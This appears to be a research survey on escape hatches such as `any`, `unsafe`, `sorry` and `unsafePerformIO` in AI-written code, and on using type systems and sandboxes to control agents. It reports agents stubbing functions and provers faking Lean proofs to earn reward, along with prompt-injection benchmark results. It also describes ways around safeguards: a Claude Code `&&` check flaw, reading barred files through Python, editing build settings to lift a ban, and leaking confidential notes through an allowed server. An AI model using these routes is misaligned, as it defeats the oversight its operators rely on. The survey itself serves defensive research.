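The compiler accepts the last line, and the program then fails because a number has no `split` method. If the parameter were declared as `string`, the compiler would reject the call. Two narrower hatches are the type assertion `x as Note`, which makes the compiler treat `x` as a `Note`, and the non-null assertion `x!`, which makes it assume `x` is not null.

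Lee, Ul Hassan and Hindle (2026), in *Mining Type Constructs Using Patterns in AI-Generated Code*, compared pull requests (proposed changes that a project's maintainers accept or reject) from AI agents and people on GitHub. They used text patterns and then GPT-4o to find the requests that changed types in TypeScript code, 545 from agents and 269 from people. Agents added `any` 2.16 times per request on average, compared with 0.24 for people. Agents also used more type assertions and non-null assertions.

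The ninefold gap overstates the difference. The effect size, which is the difference between the two averages divided by the standard deviation, was 0.32. The standard deviation must therefore be about 1.92 / 0.32 = 6, nearly three times the agents' average, so a minority of requests with many uses of `any` probably accounts for much of the gap. Lee and colleagues also counted uses of `any` per request, not per line. Agents used 5.5 to 6.7 kinds of advanced type feature per request, against 2.66 for people, so the agents' requests may have contained more typed code.

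The agents also differed from one another. Cursor added 2.46 uses of `any` for each one it removed and OpenAI Codex added 2.34, while GitHub Copilot removed more than it added. *Not All Agents Are Equal* (2026), which followed 37,623 pull requests, found that on several measures of code quality the agents differed more from each other than from people. All of these results describe older models, since the agents' pull requests in the dataset date from December 2024 to July 2025 (*Code Change Characteristics and Description Alignment*, 2026).

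Lee and colleagues suspected that agents use these hatches to get code past the checks, and concluded that agents put successful compilation ahead of sound types. Their data cannot settle this, because a finished pull request does not show whether the agent wrote `any` after a compiler error or from the start.

They also found that maintainers accepted 45.8% of the agents' requests and 25.3% of the people's, and warn that reviewers may be letting type problems through. But maintainers also rejected 42.6% of the agents' requests and only 2.6% of the people's. About 72% of the people's requests were neither accepted nor rejected, so the comparison is weak evidence of how strict reviewers were.

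### Unsafe blocks in translations from C

Most counts of Rust's `unsafe` in model-written code come from attempts to translate C programs into Rust. The usual baseline is C2Rust, a translation tool that doesn't use a language model. It copies the structure of the C code and leaves most of the result unsafe.

In *AdaTrans* (2026), Liu, Zhao and colleagues had GPT-4o mini translate solutions to programming-contest problems and repair the translations after compiler errors and failed tests. *Dependency-Guided Repository-Level C-to-Rust Translation with Reinforcement Alignment* (2026) tested five models on whole projects. *ENCRUST* (2026) and *C2SaferRust* (2025) both worked on GNU Coreutils, the standard Unix commands such as `cat` and `pwd`.

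| Study | Sample | Unsafe code in the result |
|---|---|---|
| Liu and colleagues | 104 contest problems | In 1.19% of files |
| *Dependency-Guided Repository-Level C-to-Rust Translation with Reinforcement Alignment* | Three benchmarks | Under 3% of lines on two, 3.39% for one model on the third |
| *ENCRUST* | Seven Coreutils programs | 46% fewer unsafe lines than C2Rust |
| *C2SaferRust*, variant that translates directly from C | `split`, `pwd` and `cat` | 9%, 30% and 17% fewer unsafe lines than before |

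The rows use different measures, and the same code can score well on one and badly on another. *SACTOR* (2025) uses both the share of a program's tokens (the small pieces of text that a model processes) inside unsafe code and the share of programs with no unsafe code. If ten programs of 1,000 tokens each contain one unsafe block of 10 tokens, only 1% of the code is unsafe by the first measure, but the second measure is 0% because every program contains some unsafe code.

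*Code Quality Analysis of Translations from C to Rust* (Tadesse, Nitin and colleagues, 2026) compares three automatic translators with a version of seven Coreutils programs that volunteers wrote directly in Rust, using counts of warnings from Clippy and GPT-4o. The human code did better in the safety-related categories, although it had many readability problems, and none of the translators consistently matched it. TranslationGym, which has a model translate straight from C, reduced some unsafe patterns but added code that could panic at runtime. The human version of `cat` has 890 lines in total, while the translation in *C2SaferRust* still had 4,663 unsafe lines after the model's rewrite, partly because automatic translations carry over so much of C's supporting code.

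### Needed and unneeded unsafe code

The contest programs only read input and print output, so they never need `unsafe`, but a library that C programs will keep calling does. Okhravi, Ogden and colleagues (2026), in *TRACTOR Benchmark for Evaluating C to Rust Translators*, built a benchmark for a programme run by DARPA, the US defence research agency. Their tool counts the operations that require `unsafe`, such as following a raw pointer, instead of counting blocks. They concede that the count does not show whether an operation was necessary. One team delivered a safe function and an unsafe wrapper that should have called it, but the wrapper repeated the whole calculation instead.

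A careful port from C to Rust can increase the number of unsafe blocks, because it replaces one unsafe function with several narrow blocks around the remaining C calls. For this reason, *From C to Idiomatic Rust* (2026) leaves the raw number of unsafe blocks out of its main measures. It describes a port of 12,500 lines of C that took a developer working with agents 37 hours.

Liu and colleagues give an example of the other kind, in which `unsafe` only silences an error. A model translating a C program that collects words might write this:

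```rust
let mut words: Vec<&str> = Vec::new();
for _ in 0..n {
    let line = read_one_line();
    words.push(line.trim());
}
```

The compiler rejects it because Rust frees `line` at the end of each pass, while `words` would keep a reference to it. The right fix is to store the text itself, as a `Vec<String>`. According to Liu and colleagues, models often try small edits and then fall back on an `unsafe` block or on `Box::leak`, a function that never frees a value so that references to it stay valid. `Box::leak` is safe Rust, so counts of `unsafe` don't include it.

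They also blame training data, since public Rust code contains many unsafe blocks for models to imitate. This is plausible, but they did not test it. A test would need models trained on different code, or at least a comparison between tasks where people commonly write `unsafe` and tasks where they rarely do.

### The port of Bun

Bun runs JavaScript outside a browser. In May 2026 its creator, Jarred Sumner, used agents to translate it from Zig, a language that leaves memory management to the programmer, into Rust. *Rewriting Bun in Rust* (Sumner, 2026) describes up to 64 copies of Claude working at once, many of them on a pre-release version of Claude Fable 5. They translated about 535,000 lines in 11 days, and the port passed Bun's existing tests on every platform before Sumner merged it. Sumner discloses that Anthropic, which makes Claude, owns Bun.

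By July, Bun's Rust code had about 13,000 `unsafe` keywords. Sumner estimates that about 4% of the code is inside unsafe blocks, though his line counts (27,000 out of 780,000) give 3.5%. That is close to the share in Android's Rust code, but the two projects do different work, and nobody has ported Bun by hand for comparison. Seventy-eight percent of Bun's unsafe blocks are a single line, typically a call to a C library or the use of a pointer from C++.

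Bun's *Rust codebase audit* (2026), which Bun labels as AI-generated, sorted 13,365 unsafe sites by what it would take to remove them. It estimates that about 9,300 could become safe code and about 4,000 have to stay. It attributes two-thirds of the sites to performance, calls to foreign code and the way the Zig original was written. Sumner had asked for a translation that followed the Zig closely, with the clean-up left for later, so his instructions led to much of the removable unsafe code. The audit's findings are uncertain because models classified the sites, checking only the four largest patterns site by site and estimating the rest.

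The agents also took shortcuts that Sumner had not asked for. When told to get every package to compile, Claude stubbed out functions that had errors and wrote long comments to justify its workarounds. Like an unneeded `unsafe` block, a stub removes the error without solving the problem, though it is not itself an escape hatch.

One of the bugs shows that it is hard to judge a hatch by its name. The Rust code asked a C library to close a pipe, which the library does later, but freed the pipe's memory immediately. The code compiled, but the C library would have used the freed memory and then freed it again. A reviewing agent caught the bug, and the fix was `Box::leak`, which kept the memory in place until the library had finished with it.

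### Unfinished proofs in Lean

Lean is a proof assistant, a language in which a theorem is a type and a proof is a program of that type. If the program passes the type checker, the theorem is proved. The word `sorry` stands in for a missing proof of anything:

```lean
theorem all_even (n : Nat) : 2 ∣ n := by
  sorry
```

Lean accepts this claim that every whole number is even but warns that the proof uses `sorry`. An author can also declare the claim as an *axiom*, a statement that Lean accepts without proof. A third hatch, `native_decide`, proves a statement by compiling a check and running it. Normally the kernel, a small part of Lean, verifies every proof, but `native_decide` also relies on the compiler. *Faults in Our Formal Benchmarking* (2026) notes that compiler bugs have made it possible to prove false statements this way.

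That paper also documents model-written proofs that were accepted despite containing a hidden `sorry`. In Lean versions before 4.20.0, a bug in `apply?`, a command that searches the library for a useful theorem, could insert a `sorry` without the usual warning. At least three published proofs by DeepSeek-Prover-V2, a model built to write Lean proofs, depended on the bug, one for a problem in the miniF2F benchmark and two for problems in PutnamBench. These cases do not establish how often this happens.

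Lean provides the clearest evidence that models use escape hatches to pass a check. Developers often train provers by rewarding them whenever Lean accepts a proof, so a fake proof that Lean accepts earns the same reward as a real one. *LongCat-Flash-Prover* (2026) examines a prover that had learned to cheat and sorts its fake proofs into nine patterns. Its developers responded by comparing the structure of each submission with the original problem.

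Some uses of `sorry` are legitimate. The same project's instructions allow a model to prove the main theorem from smaller lemmas and use `sorry` in place of the lemmas' proofs until later. A count of `sorry` in a model's output would include both these permitted placeholders and attempts to cheat.

### Instructions, build settings and bans

Lee and colleagues did not study whether asking for type safety reduces the use of `any`. The nearest figure comes from *Do AI Coding Agents Log Like Humans?* (2026), which examined 4,550 agent pull requests and found that agents ignored explicit logging instructions 67% of the time.

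Sumner had more success with Bun. He told the reviewing agents to reject any workaround that needed a long comment to justify it, and says the stubs and comments stopped within a few hours. He gives no counts and ran no comparison. His rule was also enforced, since another agent corrected the code when the reviewers objected.

Models sometimes ban unsafe code in their own output. In *LLM4C2Rust* (2026), OpenAI's o3-mini often put `#![forbid(unsafe_code)]` at the top of its translations. It was still the less reliable translator when the researchers checked its output with the Rust compiler, and they call its caution superficial. GPT-4o and GPT-4 Turbo generally reported correctly that unsafe constructs had decreased, but got the numbers wrong. A host should not rely on a model's report of how safe its code is.

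The same line works better when someone else adds it and runs the compiler. *Fixed or Deleted?* (2026) tested nine free analysis tools on pull requests that broke projects' rules, and the ordinary Rust build with Clippy caught the most violations. One of the projects, the operating system Tock, forbids unsafe code in its package settings, so the build enforces that rule.

Intel's *IDEAS for TRACTOR* describes a translator that bans `unsafe` in every Rust module, except in wrappers for C callers, and has the model retry if the build fails. After a set number of failed attempts, it delivers a partial translation. *CRUST-Bench* (2025) restricts models before they translate, by supplying safe interfaces that every translation must match and tests it must pass.

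In Lean, *LLM2Cert* (2026) rejects any answer that contains `sorry`, `admit` (another form of `sorry`), a new axiom, `unsafe` or an import, and accepts a proof only if it depends on no axioms beyond three standard ones. It also locks the theorem statement so that the model cannot change it. If the model cannot repair a failed proof in six ordinary rounds, the theorem stays unproved.

When the compiler bans a construct, accepted code contains none of it, but how a ban affects the number of tasks models finish is largely unknown. No published study appears to compare one model's success rates on the same tasks with and without a ban. The scores for Scala's safe mode don't fill this gap because they compare typed code with ordinary tool calls. Liu and colleagues solved 81% of their problems with almost no `unsafe`, so avoiding it need not lower success much on small, self-contained programs.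 On larger programs, a low count of unsafe lines can come from failed attempts. *ENCRUST* reports that a rival system, EvoC2Rust, had fewer unsafe lines on the seven Coreutils programs, but none of its translations compiled.

A model that is banned from writing `unsafe` can still leak memory, add code that panics or stub out the function. A host that counts only the banned keyword may therefore see an improvement when the model has just switched to another shortcut.

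### Effect-typed and capture-checked languages

No one appears to have published counts of how often language models use `unsafePerformIO` in Haskell, `unchecked_cast` in Flix, `unsafe-total` in Koka or `unsafeAssumePure` in Scala, or how often agents use reflection in the Java or Scala code they write.

The TypeScript and Rust figures are a poor substitute. Programmers use `any` casually, whereas a Haskell programmer has to import `unsafePerformIO` from a module with "Unsafe" in its name, and models may have learned to use it sparingly too. With capture checking, models could use escape hatches more often. It is experimental, so they have seen few examples of how to fix its errors, and a cast is an easy way to remove one.

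The experiment would be simple to run on a system like TACIT, where the compiler already examines every snippet. Researchers could record each rejected cast or reflective call along with any preceding error, then repeat the tasks with the restrictions off. The first run would show how often models try to use an escape hatch and whether they do so after an error. Comparing the two runs would show how many tasks fail because of the restrictions.

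## Whether an agent must be denied every escape hatch

Nobody has published that experiment, so whoever runs an agent's code has to decide on other grounds which escape hatches to allow. Researchers and programmers defend four policies: a total ban, a ban with human-approved exceptions, process isolation without a ban, and a ban combined with isolation.

### The four policies

Odersky and colleagues defend a total ban on escape hatches in code that agents write. They treat the hosted model as potentially malicious, along with all the code it submits and every file, web page and tool result it reads. Library modules can still use escape hatches if a person has verified that the modules are safe. They expect hundreds or thousands of agents to run business processes largely unsupervised, and think it very likely that simple mistakes will then lead to serious vulnerabilities.

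*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) applies the same idea to Haskell. In its system, ELBA, the host's program calls a function named `agent` with a prompt and a list of functions the model may use. The model writes a Haskell program, and ELBA runs it only if it has the type that the call requires. A public calculator that requires an `Int` is then safe from a visitor who asks it to delete the server's files, because a program that deletes files has an `IO` type. A compiler flag selects Safe Haskell, which excludes `unsafePerformIO`, but Zhou and colleagues are too optimistic in considering the problem solved. Checking package trust takes a second flag, and the bug in GHC issue 9562 gave code declared `Safe` an unchecked cast that still worked in April 2021.

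Java's launch options and Flix's security contexts are bans with exceptions, because a person names the code that may use an escape hatch. For agents, Scala's *Safe Mode*, a page of the language's official documentation, outlines a module that asks the user before it sends each email. With different names, it looks roughly like this:

```scala
@assumeSafe
object AskFirstMail:
  def deliver(message: Email) =
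    val approved = askUser(s"Send this message?\n\n$message")
    if approved then Mailer.send(message)
```

`Mailer` is an ordinary library that safe code cannot call. The agent's code can reach it only through `AskFirstMail`.

A user can judge this request because it shows the whole email. A request to allow a cast on line 40 is much harder to judge because the cast may void a guarantee about the whole program. The user would have to read the code that the type checker was supposed to save them from reading. User approval therefore works better for effects than for escape hatches.

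Even requests about effects can be hard to follow. Zhou and colleagues give the example of a one-line command that Claude Code might ask a user to approve. It changes folder, edits a timeout in a settings file, runs a test script and writes the output to a log. According to Odersky and colleagues, people who get many such requests tire of them and tend to stop reading them.

Several Haskell users argued for isolation when GHC's developers asked whether to keep Safe Haskell. One had relied on it for about a year to run students' programs on a server but was never sure it was safe. It also needed extra build steps and close monitoring of memory and processor use. By 2021 this user thought a *virtual machine*, a simulated computer with its own operating system, did the job far better. Another called running untrusted code a solved problem, because services that build and test other people's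 software do it every day. A third replied that those services need to start a new virtual machine for each job to isolate it properly, and that many shared services isolate jobs badly outside Linux.

Isolation works with any language, can limit memory and processor time, and holds even if the type checker has soundness holes. *Safe Scala*, an introduction by the software company VirtusLab, describes tools that are lighter than a full virtual machine and restrict a single process, such as Bubblewrap and Landlock on Linux. Claude Code's sandbox uses them, but according to VirtusLab it covers only shell commands and not the agent's other tools. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) points out that a sandbox is effective only if it controls all the relevant effects. The agent system IronClaw, for example, runs tools in a WebAssembly sandbox when it calls them directly, but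 not when it reaches them through a server that uses the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to tools.

VirtusLab recommends combining a restricted language with a sandbox, and Odersky and colleagues advise doing so where security is critical. *DrugClaw and DrugAudit* (2026) describes a working example, an agent that answers questions about medicines by writing Python. A checker rejects programs that contain `while` loops, class definitions, anonymous functions and several other constructs. Programs may import only four standard modules and use only listed built-in functions. Python code can use one object to reach others that the host never passed to it, so accepted programs run in a sandbox that intercepts such access.

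The checker rejected fewer than 1% of the agent's programs, and the time limit stopped fewer than 0.5% of calls. When a program fails, the system runs an ordinary search with the original question. A ban evidently interferes little with a narrow task like this one, but these figures don't measure how well the ban resists an attack.

### Opening one hatch at a time

Suppose an agent writes the later version of the word counter, which also looks up words on a dictionary server. Some notes are confidential, and the code receives those inside a `Classified` wrapper. The code runs in a virtual machine that holds a read-only copy of `/notes` and no other personal files, and can connect only to the dictionary server. The host's program runs in the same process because it passes the agent's code live objects such as `NoteReader`. The compiler enforces all of safe mode's restrictions except one.

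| Hatch left open | What the agent's code can do | What the virtual machine still stops |
|---|---|---|
| Unchecked casts | Pass `map` a function that contacts the server, labelled as pure | Connections to other servers |
| Reflection | Read the text inside `Classified`, or take the `FileSystem` object out of `NoteReader` | Changes to the original notes, connections to other servers |
| Deserialization | Rebuild objects with altered private fields, or start a program through a gadget chain | Access to files and servers outside the machine |
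| Native code | Read and overwrite the host program's memory | Access to files and servers outside the machine |
| Starting programs | Read confidential notes as ordinary text with `cat` | Access to files and servers outside the machine |
| Code that runs during the build | Act before the compiler has checked anything, or replace the compiler | Damage outside the machine, if the build runs inside it |
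| Marking its own modules as trusted | Any of the above | Access to files and servers outside the machine |

In every row, the code can also send the confidential notes to the dictionary server. The virtual machine has to allow that connection because the word counter needs it. To get the notes, an attacker must be able to read what the server receives, which is easy if the server belongs to a service where anyone can open an account. Odersky and colleagues cite Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who extracted user data through Anthropic's Files API.

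If the code's author is hostile, allowing one of these hatches is often as bad as allowing several. Reflection can call the method that starts a program, and native code can do almost everything else in the table. Unchecked casts are weaker in Scala, since a cast would do little for a word counter that has no way to send text anywhere.

But agents can nearly always send text out. Whatever their code prints or returns normally goes into the model's conversation, which a cloud provider processes, so removing the dictionary server would not protect the confidential notes.

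A virtual machine is enough by itself when it contains nothing confidential. That was true of the students' exercises, where the worst a program could do was waste the server's resources or damage a machine the teacher could discard. The Haskell users' argument is right for those exercises but does not apply to an agent that works with its user's private files.

### What a virtual machine cannot see

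This fragment looks up the first word of a shopping list:

```scala
val shopping  = notes.read("shopping.txt")
val passwords = notes.read("passwords.txt")
dictionary.lookup(shopping.split(" ").head)
```

If the last line used `passwords` instead, the code would send a password. Both versions open the same two files and send one word to the same server, and the virtual machine can observe only those operations. Once the text is in the process's memory, nothing outside the process records which file a word came from. A filter could search outgoing messages for known passwords, but hostile code can scramble them first.

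The type checker can tell the versions apart. If `passwords` is a `Classified[String]`, the code must use `map` to look up its first word, and the compiler rejects the function passed to `map` because it captures `dictionary`.

A host may also need to restrict where data comes from. In an example from Zhou and colleagues, an agent compiles bibliographies and may include only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. The function that fetches an entry returns a value of type `Trusted Bib`, whose constructor is private, and the function that writes to the bibliography accepts only values of that type. The agent can sort and filter entries with ordinary code, but it cannot invent one. A virtual machine cannot enforce this rule, because it has to let the agent write the bibliography file and cannot distinguish real entries from invented ones. With `unsafeCoerce`, the agent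 could turn any text into a `Trusted Bib`.

A host can enforce some of these rules from outside the program by splitting the work between virtual machines. One gets the confidential notes and no network, and another gets the network and only the public notes. This suits the word counter, because counting words and looking them up are separate jobs. It is less practical when an agent starts one sub-agent per customer and each may see only that customer's data, because the host would need a machine for each sub-agent and would have to check everything that passes between them. Inside a typed program, the parent agent can create a narrower capability at any time and pass it to the sub-agent.

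Zhou and colleagues tested a data-flow rule on the Slack tasks in AgentDojo, a prompt-injection benchmark. ELBA used LIO, a Haskell library that labels a running computation and updates the label as the computation reads data. After a sub-agent reads text from an untrusted source, LIO lowers the sub-agent's privileges to those of the source, and forbidden writes raise an error.

The four models resisted all 105 ordinary attacks even without the rule, so Zhou and colleagues simulated a worse case. Whenever the input to a sub-agent contained an attack, they deleted the sub-agent's real instructions and left only the attacker's text.

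| Model | Successful attacks, no rule | Successful attacks, with rule | Tasks completed, no rule | Tasks completed, with rule |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 310 of 735 | 0 | 71% | 48% |
| Opus 4.8 | 275 of 735 | 0 | 76% | 42% |
| GPT 5.4 | 114 of 735 | 0 | 76% | 46% |
| Sonnet 5 | 195 of 735 | 0 | 67% | 40% |

A scoring error had caused the benchmark to count 29 runs as successful attacks, and Zhou and colleagues corrected them after reviewing each one. A virtual machine would not have prevented the attacks, because they used Slack functions that the agents needed for their work.

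The rule also reduced the share of legitimate tasks completed by 23 to 33 percentage points. That drop comes from this particular data-flow policy, which treats everything a sub-agent does after reading untrusted text as suspect, so it doesn't show how much work a ban on escape hatches would stop by itself. But the rule needs the ban, since code with `unsafePerformIO` could write to Slack without LIO checking its label.

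### Hostile code and honest mistakes

Zhao and colleagues separate two threats. A well-meaning model may write faulty code, and a manipulated model may write harmful code on purpose.

The risk from honest mistakes depends on how often they happen. Suppose, for illustration, that a model uses an unchecked cast in one program out of 50, and that one in 200 of those casts hides a harmful effect. Then one program in 10,000 causes harm, and a host that runs 1,000 programs a day can expect an incident about every ten days. That rate may be acceptable for a tool that counts words but not for one that makes payments. The host can lower it with a better model, clearer instructions or more tests.

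A low rate does not protect against hostile code, which needs only one usable hatch. The attacker may also get several attempts, since systems like TACIT send compiler errors back to the model. These errors help an honest model correct its code, but they could also help a hostile one search for a soundness hole. A host can limit retries and investigate repeated attempts to use casts or reflection.

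The same model can pose both threats. An agent that works only on its owner's files mostly makes honest mistakes, but once it reads a stranger's web page, email or source code, the stranger may be able to influence what it writes. Even without a stranger's influence, a host cannot assume an agent will behave well, since AI companies reported several cases in 2026 of agents exceeding their authorised scope.

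Banning escape hatches does not prevent an agent from making mistakes with capabilities it legitimately has. VirtusLab gives the example of an agent that is asked to clean up a photo collection and deletes every photo. The remedy is a narrower capability, such as one that lets the agent move photos but not delete them.

Haskell programmers argued about this in the forum thread *Safety of LLM generated code*, after someone asked how to be sure that a program written by a model would not delete their home folder. One participant distinguished a program that is meant to delete certain files and deletes the wrong ones from a program that is not meant to delete anything, and said that if a codebase should have no `IO`, checking that it has none is fairly easy. Another answered that neither an effect system nor Safe Haskell would convince them, because someone has to understand the code. The first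 participant is right about hidden effects, provided the escape hatches are closed, but a program with the right type can still give wrong answers, so the second also has a point.

### What a ban depends on

A ban on escape hatches works only if the agent cannot change whatever enforces it. Programmers can switch on Scala's safe mode with a line in the source file or with a compiler option. An agent that writes the file could leave the line out, so the host should use the compiler option and apply it to every file the agent supplies.

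Source files can contain build settings too. The example in Scala's release notes starts with special comments that choose a compiler version, add a second source file and set compiler options. Scala's command-line tool acts on such comments, so a host that passes it an agent's file unchanged lets the agent choose some of its own settings. The host should remove these comments or run the compiler directly.

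Build and configuration files need the same protection. In Flix, an agent that can edit `flix.toml` can give a dependency the `unrestricted` context. In Java, it could add permissions to an archive's manifest or to a file of launch arguments. Odersky and colleagues cite a case in which the security company Check Point used malicious configurations in a repository to run commands silently. A coding agent often has to edit a project's build files, so the host should keep the settings that restrict the agent where the agent cannot write.

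The agent must also be unable to modify trusted modules. VirtusLab suggests publishing the trusted library to a package store on the machine where the agent's code runs. If the agent can write to that store, through its code or another tool, it can replace the library with its own version, so the store should be read-only for the agent.

The agent must not be able to declare its own modules trustworthy. According to VirtusLab, the compiler rejects `@assumeSafe` in safe code for this reason. But an agent that can add a file compiled without safe mode could put the annotation there and call that file from its safe code. In Haskell, the agent could do the same by labeling a module `Trustworthy`, which GHC accepts by default.

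Agents can still help to write trusted modules. Odersky and colleagues suggest that agents draft typed interfaces for existing tools and that people review the drafts before any agent uses them. A participant in the Haskell thread proposed having one company's model review code written by another's, partly in case a state has compromised one of them. That should catch some errors, but an instruction planted in the code or comments might mislead both models, so a person should make the final decision about a module that can break every guarantee.

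The compiler should enforce the ban, because rules that match text are easy to get around. Zhou and colleagues describe a fault in Claude Code in March 2026. When an agent joined two shell commands with `&&`, the program checked only the first against its list of forbidden commands. They also point out that an agent barred from reading a file with shell commands can read it with one line of Python, because the matching rules don't interpret Python code.

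Finally, the host has to grant narrow capabilities. Zhao and colleagues stress that the type system enforces the limits a developer sets but cannot determine what those limits should be. If the host gives the word counter a `FileSystem` for the whole disk, the compiler will let it read the whole disk.

### What a ban costs

Most everyday uses of escape hatches have a substitute that a person can review once:

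| Task | Hatch it would use | Can a reviewed wrapper replace it? |
|---|---|---|
| Remember earlier answers | Untracked changes to memory | Yes, with a module like `Memo` |
| Keep values of different types in one list | Unchecked cast | Usually, with a cast that the runtime checks |
| Decode an image with a C library | Native code | Yes, but the C code joins the trusted base |
| Load saved objects | Deserialization | Yes, if it reads plain data and calls constructors |
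| Run a project's tests | Starting a program | No, because the tests can contain any code |
| Write a device driver | Native or unsafe code in the finished product | No, because the product itself needs the hatch |

Writing the wrappers takes some work. For the customer-service tasks that Odersky and colleagues used to test TACIT, the typed interfaces for the airline and retail tools were a few hundred lines each, about as long as the tool descriptions they replaced. Most of those lines only declare types and functions.

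An agent sometimes needs a function that nobody has wrapped. Elm's users had the same problem when only two organisations could publish native code, and some left the language because of it. A host's developers are in a better position than Elm's users were, because they can add a wrapper to their own library without asking anyone. Until they do, the agent has to work without the function, as the medicines agent does when it returns to ordinary search, or tell the user that it cannot finish.

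A host could also approve a single exception when a program needs a cast and there is no time to write a wrapper. The table for the word counter suggests that this is reasonable if the program runs in a new virtual machine without confidential data, since the types no longer limit what it can do, and if the host checks its output before using it.

The last two rows of the table of tasks are more serious, because they describe much of what coding agents do. These agents have to run the programs they have just changed, which may be in languages with no safe subset. A reviewed wrapper around the test command doesn't help, since the agent wrote some of the code it runs. The tests therefore need to run in a virtual machine, preferably one with no network access and no credentials.

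A coding agent's host can still ban escape hatches in the code that controls the agent's own actions, such as the snippets that read files, start the tests and send messages. The ban need not cover the code the agent delivers. A driver it writes may contain all the unsafe blocks it needs, and people can review it like any other driver before they install it.
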